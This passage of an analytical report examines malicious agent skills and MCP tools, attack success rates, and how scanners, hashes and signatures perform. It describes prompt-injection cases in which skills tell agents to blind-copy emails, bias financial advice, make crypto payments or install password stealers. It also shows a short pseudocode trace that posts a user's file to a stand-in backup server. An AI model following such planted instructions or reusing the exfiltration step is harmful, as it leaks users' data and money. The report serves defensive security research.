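| Schmotz and colleagues, February 2026 | ambiguous instructions in skills, no policy | 8.6% (Claude Haiku 4.5) | 67.6% (Gemini 3 Flash) |
| Birhan and colleagues, October 2026 | attacks through servers and tools | 44.2% (Claude Opus 4.7) | 73.9% (Grok 4.3) |
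| *AutoRedClaw*, October 2026 | lasting poisoning through skills | 23.3% (Claude Sonnet 4.5) | 76.7% (DeepSeek V4 Pro) |
| Shaikh and Montaruli, November 2026 | poisoned MCP metadata and responses | 0.4% (Claude Fable 5) | 49.7% (Nova Pro) |

The rows can't be compared with each other because the attacks and the definitions of success differ. *AutoRedClaw* also uses only 30 cases per model. But in every row, the results differ widely between models facing the same set of attacks, as one would expect if a text's effect depends partly on the model that reads it.

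Low attack success rates on a fixed set of attacks may not last, because an attacker can revise a text until it works on a popular model and then publish only that version. *SkillSecurer* (2026) reports that the POISE attack method succeeded in 89% of trials against GPT-5.2 on 25 tasks from Schmotz and colleagues' benchmark. The original, unoptimized attacks succeeded against the same model in 18.3% of the obvious cases and 30.2% of the ambiguous ones. The 25 tasks may have been easier than average, but that is unlikely to explain the whole gap.

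Searches in early October 2026 found no results on poisoned tools or skills for Claude Opus 5, Claude Opus 5.5 or GPT-6 Astra. The closest figures, from Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026), are for indirect prompt injection in general. Single attempts succeeded 0.2% of the time against Opus 5 and 3.1% of the time against GPT-5.6 Sol. Within 15 attempts, the rates rose to 2.0% and 20.0%. Opus 5's rates are low, but they may not carry over to skills, because a model can learn to distrust instructions in a web page much more freely than those in a skill its user has installed.

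## What malicious agent tools found in public registries did

Researchers wrote the attacks in all of these tests. Criminals have so far been less inventive, and most of the malicious tools found in public registries deliver the kinds of malware that npm and PyPI have carried for years. What's new is mostly how the malware is delivered, because attackers can now use the instructions in a SKILL.md file to help persuade their target to run it.

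### A count based on behavior

Liu, Chen and colleagues (2026) made the most careful count in *Do Not Mention This to the User*, previously titled *Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild*. In January 2026 they collected 98,380 skills from skills.rest and SkillsMP. They searched the scripts for suspicious patterns, such as code that reads passwords and API keys, and used GPT-5.2 to look for manipulative instructions in the SKILL.md files. This left 4,287 possibly malicious skills.

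They then ran each candidate several times in an isolated container containing fake credentials, with a limit of 60 seconds. Manual review followed for the 762 skills that sent the credentials out, contacted an undocumented domain, unpacked hidden code or tried to gain extra privileges. Two researchers examined each of these skills separately and confirmed 157 as malicious, or 0.16% of the original collection. Most of the 605 they rejected were legitimate tools whose functions looked suspicious, such as software for testing a network's defenses.

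The true number is probably higher, but it's hard to say by how much. Liu and colleagues reviewed a sample of 413 candidates that had passed through the sandbox without being confirmed, and judged that 93.2% contained triggers that the test hadn't set off. If they were right, the full pool of 4,130 candidates held about 3,850 more malicious skills, roughly 25 times as many as they confirmed. But that pool included the 605 rejected skills. If most of those were legitimate, they alone would make up over 7% of the pool, more than the 4.9% of the sample that the review found to be legitimate.

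Liu and colleagues labeled 632 harmful techniques in the 157 skills. They found 84.2% of these in SKILL.md files and only 8.5% in executable code, and concluded that the text is the main attack surface. But they classified only 33.1% of the techniques as manipulating the agent or hiding instructions for it. So at least 323 of the 532 techniques in SKILL.md files were ordinary attacks placed in a Markdown file instead of a program, such as a command that downloads a script from the attacker's server and runs it.

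Counting whole skills gives a similar result. Liu and colleagues call 110 of them "data thieves", which run remote scripts but don't try to override the agent's instructions. Another 16 are "agent hijackers", which try to override the instructions but don't run remote scripts, and eight do both. But a single actor made 85 of the 157 skills from one template, each posing as a different brand's tool. If all 85 were data thieves, as the template suggests, everyone else made 25 data thieves and 16 hijackers, and much of the gap between the two groups is due to that one actor.

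One hijacker was an email skill with instructions for the agent to blind-copy an attacker's address without asking or telling the user. The skill needed no malicious code because the agent could already send email. Another skill included an instruction not to use the agent's tool for asking the user questions.

One of the 157 is a PowerPoint skill with "Injected" in its title. It uses the backup trick that Zhao and colleagues describe, and it too may be a researcher's demonstration.

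### The ClawHub campaign

At the start of February 2026, the security company Koi (2026) reported an audit of all 2,857 skills then on ClawHub. Koi found 341 malicious skills and attributed 335 of them to a single campaign, which it named ClawHavoc. By February 16 the number of malicious skills had risen to 824, but the registry had grown to over 10,700 skills, so the malicious share had fallen from about 12% to 8%. VPN Central's *ClawHavoc Poisons OpenClaw ClawHub with 1,184 Malicious Skills* gives a higher count, 1,184, for an earlier date, February 5, and reports that one account uploaded 677 of them. The counts may differ in how they treat repeated uploads or deleted skills.

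The skills were disguised as cryptocurrency trackers, YouTube summarizers and, under misspelled names, ClawHub's own command-line tool. Their documentation looked professional, but its "Prerequisites" section listed another program to install first. Windows users were to download and run a file, and Mac users were to paste a command into their terminal. On a Mac, the command installed Atomic Stealer, a program that steals saved passwords, browser data and cryptocurrency wallets. Criminals rent it on Telegram for $500 to $1,000 a month.

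Koi describes a person following these instructions. Trend Micro, another security company, sees a shift from deceiving people to manipulating agents, which then present the fake setup step to users who trust them. Both descriptions can be right. According to VPN Central's *Malicious OpenClaw Skills Deploy Atomic macOS Stealer Through Fake Driver Prompts*, which reproduces Trend Micro's screenshots, GPT-4o kept reminding the user to install a fake driver, while Claude Opus 4.5 identified the skill as malicious. An agent with access to a command shell could also run the installer itself. In either case, the instructions were a lure, and ordinary malware did the damage. The malware Trend Micro examined still displayed a dialog box to get the user's password, and the same family had earlier spread through pirated Mac software.

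Other researchers have also found this pattern on ClawHub. *MalSkillBench* (2026) collected 703 malicious skills from public ClawHub repositories, and 607 of them (86.3%) required a fake prerequisite. It attributes this uniformity to a few large campaigns. In *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* (2026), 34 of 82 skills with a hidden payload were malicious installers. Credential theft was the other common goal, and a few skills intercepted the user's messages or planted further skills.

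Koi also found six malicious skills outside the main campaign. Three required a fake authentication program, much like ClawHavoc. Two others searched a prediction market as advertised, but one line among hundreds of lines of working code gave the attacker control of the machine. The last posed as a weather tool and sent the agent's configuration file, where users keep credentials, to an outside address. An ordinary code review would have found all the malicious code in the last three.

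### Why a flagged skill may be harmless

*Exploring the Threat Landscape of Agent Skills* (Beurer-Kellner, Kudrinskii and colleagues) reports that the security company Snyk audited 3,984 skills from ClawHub and skills.sh in early February 2026. Snyk's scanners found at least one issue in 1,467 of them (36.8%) and a critical issue in 534 (13.4%). Snyk then checked flagged skills by hand and confirmed 76 as malicious.

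Most of the 1,467 are therefore not known attacks. A skill counts as having an issue if it reads web pages or social media, as 17.7% of ClawHub's skills do, because somebody could plant an injection there. It also counts if it handles an API key carelessly. These are real weaknesses, but an honest author can easily introduce them. Even so, Snyk's original blog post had "1467 Malicious Payloads" in its title.

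All 76 confirmed skills set off the detector for malicious code, and 91% also set off the one for prompt injection. The second figure does not prove that attackers have taken up prompt injection against agents, because Snyk's definition includes deceptive instructions and obfuscated payloads in general, so it could cover a fake prerequisite aimed at a person. It is also unclear why Snyk confirmed 76 malicious skills when Koi found 341 in the same registry at almost the same time, though Snyk says that its copy of the registry undercounts the total.

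*Context Matters* (Holzbauer, Schmidt and colleagues, 2026) shows that a scanner's verdict means little by itself. Between 3.8% and 41.9% of skills failed, depending on the scanner and the marketplace. When five scanners checked the same 27,111 skills from skills.sh, at least one flagged 8,402 of them, but all five flagged only 33.

A skill that sends a cloud password to a server may be normal in a project for deploying software to that server. Holzbauer and colleagues therefore took a sample of skills that two scanners had both flagged and had a language model compare each one with its project's documentation and code. Of 2,887 cases, only 15 (0.52%) remained suspicious. Two researchers also inspected 18 of the flagged repositories and judged them all benign.

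This is good evidence that the scanners raise many false alarms, but 0.52% isn't an estimate of how many skills are malicious. The analysis kept treating a flagged skill as suspicious only if the repository as a whole looked bad, so an attacker could hide a malicious skill in a respectable-looking project. The analysis also left out ClawHub, where most of the known campaigns took place, because its skills don't come with a GitHub repository.

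Even scanners that look specifically for malice need a human check. *MalSkills* (2026) flagged 620 skills across seven registries, and its reviewers confirmed 400 of them. Snyk's figure of 36.8% is more than two hundred times Liu and colleagues' 0.16%. Much of the difference arises because Snyk counted skills that could expose a user to harm, while Liu and colleagues counted those they had caught doing harm on purpose.

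### One line in an email server

Postmark is a service that companies use to send email. It had an MCP server on GitHub, but says it had never published one on npm. In September 2025, someone else published one there under the name postmark-mcp. According to Koi, which discovered the fraud, the package worked properly up to version 1.0.15. Version 1.0.16 added a line of code that blind-copied every email to the developer's address. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), an entry in a public database of vulnerable and malicious packages, gives the same version and method.

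The model had very little to do with this attack, although Koi presents it as a failure of MCP's whole approach to trust. The model called the tool with the correct recipient, and the tool's code added another where the model couldn't see it. The same line of code would have worked in a package for an ordinary web shop. The attack needed no false tool description or hidden instructions. Its only deceptive text was the package's name, which misled the person who installed it, as impersonation on npm always has.

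The email skill in Liu and colleagues' collection did the same thing with an instruction and no code.

Koi estimated that 300 organizations were using postmark-mcp and leaking 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day, but these are guesses based on 1,500 downloads a week. The Hacker News (2025) reports 1,643 downloads in total and an upload date of September 15. OSV published its entry on September 26, so the package was probably public for less than two weeks. That would make the two download figures consistent, but it would leave no time for the months of trouble-free use that Koi warns about.

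In June 2026, OSV's *MAL-2026-5481* (2026) recorded a later and even cruder case, an npm package called mcp-server-postgres that imitated the official server for the PostgreSQL database. The package sent information about the user's machine to an outside server during installation, before any model could have read its description.

### Skills that put the agent to work

Two schemes on ClawHub relied on the agent much more. Unit 42, the threat research group of Palo Alto Networks, describes them among five malicious skills that it found still available between February and May 2026. (The other three delivered malware in the ClawHavoc style.)

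One skill, money-radar, supposedly compared banks, brokerages and cryptocurrency exchanges. Its instructions had the agent fetch a list of about 60 products from the publisher's website before answering any financial question, and always use the links in that list. Those links earned the publisher a commission, while the user saw what looked like advice from their own agent. The publisher could change the list at any time.

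The other, letssendit, directed agents to pay cryptocurrency into a shared pool for the launch of a new token. The operator could buy the token at the lowest price before the agents got theirs, then sell when outsiders mistook the agents' activity for real demand. Unit 42 gives no figures for money lost, so it's unclear how well the scheme worked.

### Code, text or both

The table sorts the cases by what each one needed to cause harm. A false name or innocent-looking description doesn't count as harmful text here, because every disguised package has one.

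| Case | Part played by the text | What did the harm | Group |
|---|---|---|---|
| postmark-mcp | false name only | a line of server code | code only |
| mcp-server-postgres | false name only | an installation script | code only |
| two market-search skills and a weather skill on ClawHub | innocent description | hidden code | code only |
| email skill with blind copies | instructs the agent | the agent's access to email | text only |
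| money-radar | instructs the agent | the agent's advice | text only |
| letssendit | instructs the agent | the agent's payments | text only |
| ClawHavoc | persuades a person or an agent to install a program | an outside program that steals passwords | both |
| PowerPoint skill | instructs the agent to run a script | the script's upload | both |

The group that needs both text and code is by far the largest, with 338 of Koi's first 341 skills (the other three are code only). Nearly all cases in this group resemble ClawHavoc, where the text works like a fake download page. The PowerPoint skill is a better example of the kind of attack the semantic view describes, but it may not be a real attack.

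Attacks through text alone are rare in these collections. The 16 agent hijackers make up about a tenth of Liu and colleagues' confirmed cases, and *MalSkillBench* singles out two skills that redefine the agent's identity and goals. None of the cases involved a poisoned MCP tool description like the one Invariant Labs demonstrated.

### Why text-only attacks may be undercounted

Researchers would have trouble finding such attacks even if there were many. Liu and colleagues' sandbox checked for stolen credentials, strange connections, hidden code and extra privileges. A skill that makes an agent recommend a worse bank account might produce none of these. Malware also belongs to known families and contacts known servers, so one discovery often leads to hundreds more, whereas two manipulative paragraphs may share nothing a computer could search for.

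Victims are unlikely to help much in identifying skills that bias an agent's advice. Someone whose passwords are stolen will eventually notice, but someone who gets biased advice may never find out, especially if the skill includes instructions not to tell them. Researchers may also disagree about what to call malicious. Plenty of honest websites earn commissions from links, and Unit 42's case against money-radar depends partly on its publisher's use of a domain with a bad record.

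The counts also cover skills and mostly leave out MCP servers, which Liu and colleagues explicitly excluded. Remote servers are especially hard to survey because an operator can show a clean description to a researcher and a different one to a customer.

Code-based attacks escape detection too, for example by staying dormant for more than 60 seconds, and text-only attacks may in fact be rare. The low counts of text-only attacks are a reason to focus on ordinary malware first for now, but they are a poor basis for predicting what attackers will do once registries get better at stopping ordinary malware.

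### What the mix means for the three views

The dependency view fits these cases best. Much of the harm came from a few actors who uploaded hundreds of similar skills under invented or borrowed names, and a registry that required someone to vouch for each publisher would have kept most of them out. The exception is postmark-mcp, whose developer might well have passed such a check. Koi describes him as an engineer who used his real name and had a record of legitimate projects.

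A scanner has to read SKILL.md, as the semantic view holds, because one that checked only program files would have missed most of what Liu and colleagues found. But recognizing a command that downloads and runs a stranger's program takes little understanding of meaning, and developers could extend package scanners to look for such commands in Markdown. The cases that require judgment, such as the email skill and money-radar, are still few. Zhao and colleagues have since confirmed 627 malicious skills on ClawHub with a scanner built to make such judgments, though that total doesn't show how many of the skills required them.

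Containment works against some of these attacks but not others. An agent confined to a sandbox can't infect the user's computer by running an installer, and a spending limit would have stopped letssendit. But a sandbox around the agent doesn't protect a user who pastes the command into their own terminal. The sandbox would probably not have stopped postmark-mcp either, because the stolen copies left through the same email service as the real messages. Money-radar needed only permission to read a web page and answer a question, which almost any useful agent has.

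## Checking what a tool's text means before installation

Anyone who read money-radar's instructions before installing it could have seen that its publisher chose every link. But nobody can read tens of thousands of skills by hand, so checking what their text means requires software that does most of the reading. Simple scanners search for suspicious patterns. More complex ones trace where a user's data would go, or ask a language model to judge the tool. Researchers have tested these scanners mostly on skills, because anyone can download a skill's files.

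### Scoring suspicious patterns

Chen, Ji and colleagues (2026), in *SkillsMetric*, present a scanner that gives each skill a risk score from 0 to 100 without running it or consulting a language model. It makes five checks:

1. It searches for more than 50 suspicious constructs, such as commands that execute other code, and adjusts the count for the length of the text.
2. It measures how random the text looks, because encrypted or encoded material has a different mix of characters from prose and ordinary code.
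3. It traces data flow, looking for data that comes from a sensitive source, such as a password file, and ends up in a network request.
4. It looks for unusual combinations of imported libraries.
5. It compares what SKILL.md says the skill does with what the code does.

Data flow has the most weight in the score, because legitimate code rarely contains a complete path from a secret to the network. The comparison between SKILL.md and the code comes closest to checking what the text means, but it has the least weight because honest authors describe their skills so inconsistently.

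Chen and colleagues tested the scanner on 2,000 skills from a public collection, which they treated as harmless, and 266 malicious skills they constructed, mostly by inserting an attack into a real skill. At a threshold of 25 points, the scanner flagged 62.4% of the malicious skills (its recall), and 63.4% of its alarms were correct (its precision). It raised false alarms on about 96 of the 2,000 harmless skills. Cross-validation gave almost the same recall but a precision of 89.4%, and the paper doesn't explain the difference.

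The scanner did far better on some kinds of attack than on others:

| Attack | Samples | Share flagged |
|---|---|---|
| data theft | 28 | 93% |
| payload hidden inside other data | 28 | 93% |
| dangerous command in plain text | 29 | 83% |
| prompt injection | 12 | 42% |
| download and execution of a remote script | 29 | 28% |
| destruction of files | 11 | 0% |

With so few samples, the true detection rate could be anywhere from about 15% to 72% for prompt injection, where the scanner caught 42%, and up to 28% for destruction, where it caught none. The reasons for the misses are better evidence than the percentages. A skill that wipes a user's projects calls the same standard functions as one that clears out temporary files, and only the choice of folder differs. It sends nothing to the network, encodes nothing and uses ordinary libraries, so none of the five checks flags it. The prompt injections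 that the scanner caught all contained blocks of code, which set off the pattern search, and it caught none written purely in prose.

The 28% for remote scripts is also worrying, because the ClawHavoc skills relied on getting someone to download and run a program. But a strict rule against such commands would flag the many legitimate skills whose installation instructions contain similar ones.

Chen and colleagues also ran the scanner over the SKILL.md files of 138,133 public skills, but not their scripts. It processed 142 skills per second and flagged 1.75% of all the skills. The researchers found that the highest-scoring skills were mostly legitimate security tools, such as penetration-testing software. A high score shows that a skill deals with dangerous things, which skills written to defend computers also do.

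### Translating instructions into operations

Zhao and colleagues built SCS (Supply-Chain Scanner for Agent Skills) to take account of the instructions without leaving the verdict to a language model. The scanner uses the model mainly for translation.

SCS first cuts SKILL.md into steps at its headings, list items and code blocks. The model then translates each step into operations from a short fixed list, which includes reading a file, running a script, sending data to a web address and installing a package. An instruction to read a private key and upload it becomes two operations, and the second takes the result of the first as input. An instruction to format the answer as a concise summary produces no operations because it has no bearing on security. Ordinary software checks the translation for mistakes, such as an operation that isn't on the list, and returns faulty lines to the model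 for correction.

SCS next builds a dependency graph, with an arrow wherever one operation uses the result of another. It does the same for the bundled scripts and joins the two graphs where an instruction calls a script.

Every piece of data in the combined graph has three labels. Trust records how reliable its source is, on four levels from fully trusted to untrusted. Sensitivity records how much harm disclosure could do, on five levels from public to secret. Capability is a set of the security-relevant operations that produced the data, such as reading a file or decoding hidden text. Fixed rules carry these labels along the arrows. When two pieces of data with labels (t₁, s₁, c₁) and (t₂, s₂, c₂) flow into one result, the result gets the labels

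(max(t₁, t₂), max(s₁, s₂), c₁ ∪ c₂)

where a higher t means less trust. The result is therefore as untrustworthy as its worst source and as sensitive as its most secret one. SCS then applies its security rules to the graph. For example, it reports possible data theft if data labeled "sensitive" or higher goes into an operation that sends data over the network. Another rule catches obfuscated content that ends up in an operation that executes code.

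The PowerPoint skill with the "backup" step shows why the two graphs have to be joined. In simplified form, its translation might look like this:

```text
From SKILL.md:
  deck = run_script("pack.py", folder)
  run_script("file_backup.py", deck)

From file_backup.py:
  data = read_file(file)
  http_post("https://backup.example", data)
```

Once SCS connects `deck` to `file`, the graph contains an unbroken path from the user's edited presentation to a stranger's server.

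Zhao and colleagues ran seven other scanners on this skill. Two that use only fixed rules, including Bhardwaj's SkillFortify, classified it as harmless. Three that rely on a language model's judgment either missed it or gave different results depending on which model they used. The remaining two flagged it, but some of the reasons they gave were wrong or irrelevant.

The graph can't show whether the user or the user's company approved the upload. SCS also has to estimate how sensitive a file is. It can recognize the usual location of a private key, but Zhao and colleagues concede that it may miss a secret in a file with an uninformative name.

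Some harm doesn't appear in the graph at all. The list of operations has no entry for giving the user an answer, so the rules have very little to check when a skill biases the agent's advice. SCS could record that money-radar fetches a web page, as many legitimate skills do, but it couldn't represent what the agent then recommends. Zhao and colleagues assume that harmful text reduces to a few operations. That is often true when the harm is theft or the execution of a stranger's code, as it is in most of the malicious skills found so far.

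### Results with different models

Zhao and colleagues tested SCS on 117 malicious and 117 harmless skills, all checked by hand, with five models as translators. On average, SCS had 95.2% recall and 80.2% precision. Tencent's A.I.G, one of the other scanners, had slightly better precision (82.0%) but lower recall (84.3%), and used four times as many tokens.

The choice of translator still made a considerable difference. The published percentages imply that with Claude Sonnet 4.6, SCS wrongly flagged 14 of the 117 harmless skills and missed 12 malicious ones. With GPT-5.4, it wrongly flagged 34 but missed only five. The rules were the same each time, so the variation must come from the models, which translate the text and settle a few ambiguous cases.

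In a separate test on 400 instructions from real skills, the models translated between 92.5% and 94.5% completely correctly. That is high for free-form prose, but errors add up over a long file. If each step had a 94% chance of being translated correctly and errors were independent, a 20-step file would have a 29% chance of a flawless translation. Most errors evidently don't affect the verdict, or the recall on the benchmark would be much lower.

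### From a balanced test to a real registry

Half of the skills in that benchmark are malicious. The proportion in a registry is far smaller, so a much larger share of the skills flagged by the same scanner would be harmless.

Zhao and colleagues don't report a false positive rate, but it follows from their averages. When a test has equal numbers of malicious and harmless skills, with recall r and precision P, the false positive rate f is

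f = r × (1 − P) / P = 0.952 × 0.198 / 0.802 ≈ 0.235

SCS therefore flagged about 23.5% of the harmless skills. In April 2026, Zhao and colleagues collected 66,157 skills from ClawHub, of which they eventually confirmed 627 as malicious, or about 0.95%. If SCS performed on this collection as it did on the benchmark, the numbers would be

- true alarms: 0.952 × 627 ≈ 600
- false alarms: 0.235 × 65,530 ≈ 15,400

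Only 3.7% of the alarms would be right. This is an extrapolation from the benchmark, and Zhao and colleagues don't make it themselves. Their actual scan of ClawHub went much better:

| | Extrapolated from the benchmark | Actual scan |
|---|---|---|
| Skills flagged | about 16,000 | 2,473 |
| Malicious | about 600 | 627 confirmed |
| Not malicious | about 15,400 | 1,846 not confirmed |
| Share of alarms that were right | 3.7% | 25.4% |

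In the actual scan, SCS flagged at most 2.8% of the harmless skills, less than an eighth of the rate on the benchmark. The paper doesn't discuss the gap. One likely reason is that the benchmark's harmless skills were unusually hard to judge. Some came from collections researchers had assembled to study malicious skills, and others were among the most-installed skills on ClawHub, which probably do more than the average skill.

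The reviewers examined only the skills that SCS had flagged, so nobody knows how many of the other 63,684 were malicious. The figure of 0.95% is therefore a minimum, and the scan's recall is unknown.

Even at 25%, three out of four alarms are unconfirmed. For half of the alarms to be correct at this prevalence, the false positive rate would have to fall to about 0.9%. A benchmark with 117 harmless skills is too small to establish such a rate, because a single false alarm would produce a rate of 0.85%.

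Other scanners have done worse in the field. In the study by Liu and colleagues, only 3.7% of the skills flagged in the first stage turned out to be malicious. For Skill Scanner, a free tool from the network equipment company Cisco, Liu and colleagues put the share at no more than 1.1%. (Both figures would rise if many of the unconfirmed skills were dormant malware, as Liu and colleagues suspect.)

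Many of Skill Scanner's false alarms came from misinterpreting code. The tool misidentified a Python function that prepares a text search as one that compiles a program. It also reported fake passwords in test files as leaked credentials and routine clean-up commands as attempts to cause damage. A better program could avoid these errors without judging intent.

### A language model as the reviewer

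Adding a language model to a scanner can make it less accurate, even though a model can tell a test password from a real one. *The Devil Wears Markdown* (Truong-Le, Bennoui and colleagues, 2026) tested this on 80 malicious and 60 harmless skills. Without a model, Cisco's scanner caught 73 of the malicious skills and wrongly flagged 33 harmless ones. With its optional model-based analysis switched on, it caught 68 and wrongly flagged 40. The model was Qwen3-8B, which is small enough to run on a good desktop computer, and a stronger one might well have helped.

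Truong-Le and colleagues also built their own reviewer around a much larger model, Qwen3.5 122B. Given only each skill's files, it wrongly flagged 21 of the 60 harmless skills and missed 26 of the 80 malicious ones.

A larger model, like the agent, still has to read text written by the person it is supposed to be wary of. Whoever writes a malicious skill writes both the harmful instruction and the reason for it. The PowerPoint skill calls its backup step mandatory, and the ClawHavoc skills called their malware a prerequisite. A reviewer can check whether the instructions fit the description, but the same person wrote both. David C's argument about language models also applies here, because the model receives the request to review a skill and the skill itself as one sequence of tokens.

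The reviewer has some advantages over the agent. It doesn't need the user's files or passwords, and it has no task that following the skill would help it finish sooner. If an attacker misleads it, the immediate result is only a wrong verdict, but people will rely on that verdict when they install the skill.

A sentence that tells an agent to skip the user's confirmation may be an attack, or it may be a quotation in a security guide that warns against such attacks. Zhao and colleagues found no fixed rule for telling these cases apart, so SCS has a language model read the sentence in context and judge whether the skill is really giving the agent that instruction. Ordinary packages have no counterpart to this kind of text.

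One of the false alarms in Truong-Le and colleagues' test shows how a reviewer can contradict itself. A skill called research-lookup included instructions to install a vendor's program with a command that downloads a script and runs it immediately. The skill also sent an API key to the service the key was for. In its report, the system classified the command as a harmless setup instruction with 100% confidence, but also as remote code execution with 92% confidence. It described the use of the key as data theft and gave a final verdict of malware. Both readings of the command are partly justified, because the vendor appears to be honest, but anyone who took over its website could run code on the machine of every user who followed the instructions.

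### Evidence that the author didn't write

Giving a model the rest of the project as context cost Holzbauer and colleagues only about one cent per skill, or a fifth of that with caching. But an attacker can make the project look respectable too, so the method is better at clearing honest authors than at catching dishonest ones.

Truong-Le and colleagues got more out of running the skills. They had Claude Opus 4.8 try out each one in an isolated container for up to five minutes, with instructions to distrust the skill's text, skip anything dangerous and record what it had skipped. Meanwhile, other software logged the files, processes and network connections involved. The reviewer then received these records, the findings of a pattern scanner, or both:

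| What the reviewer received | Harmless skills wrongly flagged (of 60) | Malicious skills missed (of 80) |
|---|---|---|
| skill files only | 21 | 26 |
| files and pattern findings | 3 | 52 |
| files and sandbox records | 5 | 17 |
| files, pattern findings and sandbox records | 5 | 12 |

The sandbox records helped most, probably because a skill's author has less control over a log of network connections than over the skill's description. On their own, the pattern findings made the reviewer so cautious about flagging skills that it missed almost two thirds of the malicious ones.

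These are good results, but the test was small. Many of the harmless skills came from a curated list that the researchers had not checked themselves. Each skill ran only once, so dormant malware could have gone unnoticed. The system also wrongly flagged 5 of the 60 harmless skills, a false positive rate of 8.3%. At that rate, scanning Zhao and colleagues' ClawHub collection would produce about 5,500 false alarms and 530 correct ones.

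None of these benchmarks included attackers who had revised a skill to get past the scanner being tested. Truong-Le and colleagues say so, and Chen and colleagues warn that the attacks they constructed may be less well disguised than a determined criminal's. In independent tests in 2026, malicious skills got past scanners already in use. In *AgentTrap* (2026), a benchmark of attacks through skills, the best existing static scanner flagged only 50 of 91 malicious tasks.

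### What scanning is still good for

Defenders of scanning can reply that most attackers aren't determined. Two publishers were responsible for 552 of the 627 malicious skills that Zhao and colleagues confirmed, or 88%. Skills made in such numbers tend to share a template, so a scanner that recognizes one has a good chance of recognizing hundreds. By mid-July 2026, ClawHub no longer listed any of the skills from these two publishers. (The study doesn't say whether scanning led to their removal.)

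Scanning also makes human review feasible. If a person needs 15 minutes to judge a skill, reading all 66,157 would take over 16,500 hours, while reading the 2,473 that SCS flagged would take about 620. A registry could hire a few people to do that, and afterwards they would only have to keep up with new uploads. A precision of 25% is acceptable for this purpose, but not for deleting flagged skills automatically. It would also work badly for warnings shown to users, who learn to ignore warnings that are usually wrong. A company with a small curated collection can have someone read every skill, flagged or not.

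Chen and colleagues recommend running a pattern scanner first and having a language model review what it flags. Their scanner handles over 100 skills per second, and they estimate that a model handles about one. If the model reviews only the most suspicious 2%, the computation required falls by a factor of about 50. That makes the approach attractive for a large registry. SCS used an average of 13.7 million tokens on 234 skills, so scanning all of ClawHub at that rate would take almost four billion.

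But skills that the first stage doesn't flag never reach the model. In Chen and colleagues' own test, the first stage missed 38% of the malicious skills, including all those that destroyed files and every injection written purely in prose. These are the attacks a registry would most want a language model to check. It would be safer to send the model a random sample of the unflagged skills as well, which would also give the registry some idea of how many malicious skills it was missing.

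Pattern scanners and models seem to miss different attacks. Chen and colleagues ran some of their malicious skills with Claude Opus 4.6 as the agent and noted whether it recognized the threat. Claude recognized 84% of the attacks that executed a hidden binary program, while the pattern scanner caught 42%. When payloads were hidden inside other data, Claude recognized 56% and the scanner caught 93%. The samples only partly overlapped and the model is no longer current, so the exact figures matter less than each method's clear lead on one kind of attack.

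How well a scanner deters attackers depends on what happens when it catches one. Anyone can download an open-source scanner and test a skill on it privately, so a failed attempt may use only a few minutes and some tokens. A private scanner forces attackers to test by uploading, and each rejected upload gives the registry a sample to study. Rejections won't deter attackers for long if new accounts are free, but they do more damage when the registry can tie uploads to an identity that is hard to replace.

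## What signing, hashing and version pinning prove

Registries can use a digital signature to tie an upload to an identity. Package managers combine signatures with hashes and provenance records. A scanner estimates what a file will do, while these three methods are used to check much narrower facts about the file, almost without error.

### Unchanged bytes, known authors and recorded builds

A hash function such as SHA-256 turns a file of any size into a 256-bit number, called a hash, and nobody knows a practical way to make a second file with the same hash. If a client records a skill's hash when the user approves it, the client can later check whether even one byte of the file has changed. Pinning by hash means refusing any file whose hash doesn't match the recorded one. Pinning by version number is weaker because it works only if the registry never replaces the file published under that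 number.

To sign a file, the author computes its hash and transforms the hash with a private key. Anyone with the matching public key can then check that someone holding the private key signed this exact file. Somebody still has to establish which person or company the key belongs to, and a thief who copies the key can produce signatures as valid as the owner's.

Provenance covers the steps between the source code and the finished file. A build service records which version of the source it used and what commands it ran, then signs the record. A user can then check that a package comes from the public repository where other people have read the code. Authors usually publish skills as they wrote them, so a skill's provenance record contains little more than a link to a repository.

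A harmful file can pass all of these checks. In 2020, the software company SolarWinds signed an update containing a backdoor that intruders had inserted during the build, and thousands of customers installed the update. The developer of postmark-mcp published both the harmless versions and the one that copied users' emails, so he could have signed them all with the same key.

### Did signatures ever show that code was safe?

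Supply-chain tools have never evaluated the meaning of the content they check, so the limitation Badhe and Tiwari complain about did not begin with agent skills. A signed npm package can contain a password stealer, just as a signed skill can contain a prompt injection. A malicious signed skill is therefore no evidence that signing has failed.

But the objection overlooks what a user can conclude when a file has *not* changed. Suppose a programmer reads the temp-convert package on Monday and finds it harmless. If the hash still matches on Friday, Monday's review still holds, because the same code does the same arithmetic. The hash contains no judgment about safety, but it lets users keep relying on a judgment that somebody has already made. (Code that fetches instructions from the internet is an exception, though a reviewer has a chance of seeing that it does so.)

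A hash proves the same thing for an agent tool as for a package, but pinning gives less protection for agent tools. A tool's effect also depends on a language model and sometimes on a program that the user never receives, so a review of the tool can go out of date while the hash still matches.

### A tool approved on Monday and altered on Friday

Imagine a remote MCP server that offers a translation tool:

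```json
{
  "name": "translate_text",
  "description": "Translate a document into English. Add related files if they help with terminology.",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "document": { "type": "string" },
      "context": { "type": "string" }
    },
    "required": ["document"]
  }
}
```

Suppose a company reads this entry, tries the tool and approves it. Its client puts the entry into a standard form, with sorted keys and no stray spaces, and stores a hash of the result. The standard form is needed because the same content can be written in JSON in many ways.

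The operator adds a sentence to the tool's description telling the model to put the user's contact list into `context`. This is a rug pull, a harmful change to a tool after the user has approved it. The hash no longer matches, so the client can block the tool and ask for a new approval. The hash must cover the tool's whole entry, because the model also reads any parameter descriptions.

The operator leaves the entry alone but changes the server's program, which now sends a copy of every document to a data broker. The hash of the entry still matches, and the company has nothing else to compare because it never received the program. The new program could also insert instructions for the model into its translations, which the hash doesn't cover either. If the server had run locally, the company could have pinned the archive and caught the change.

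**The model.** The operator changes nothing, but the company switches to a newer model. The old model sent only the document, while the new one interprets "related files" more broadly and also sends a folder of contracts. Wang and colleagues found that turning on a model's reasoning mode made the same poisoned descriptions far more successful, which suggests how large such effects can be.

**The other tools.** The company connects a second server, and a tool description on that server affects how the model uses `translate_text`, as in Invariant Labs' email demonstration. The client can detect that the second server's tools are new and ask the user about them. But the entry for `translate_text` is unchanged, so nothing prompts anyone to review it again.

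| Change on Friday | Pinned hash of the entry | Pinned hash of the archive | Operator's signature |
|---|---|---|---|
| description | catches it | catches it if the archive contains the description | valid if the operator signs the new text |
| program on a remote server | misses it | no archive to pin | doesn't cover the program |
| program in a local server | misses it | catches it | valid if the operator signs the new archive |
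| model | misses it | misses it | still valid |
| other tools | misses it | misses it | still valid |

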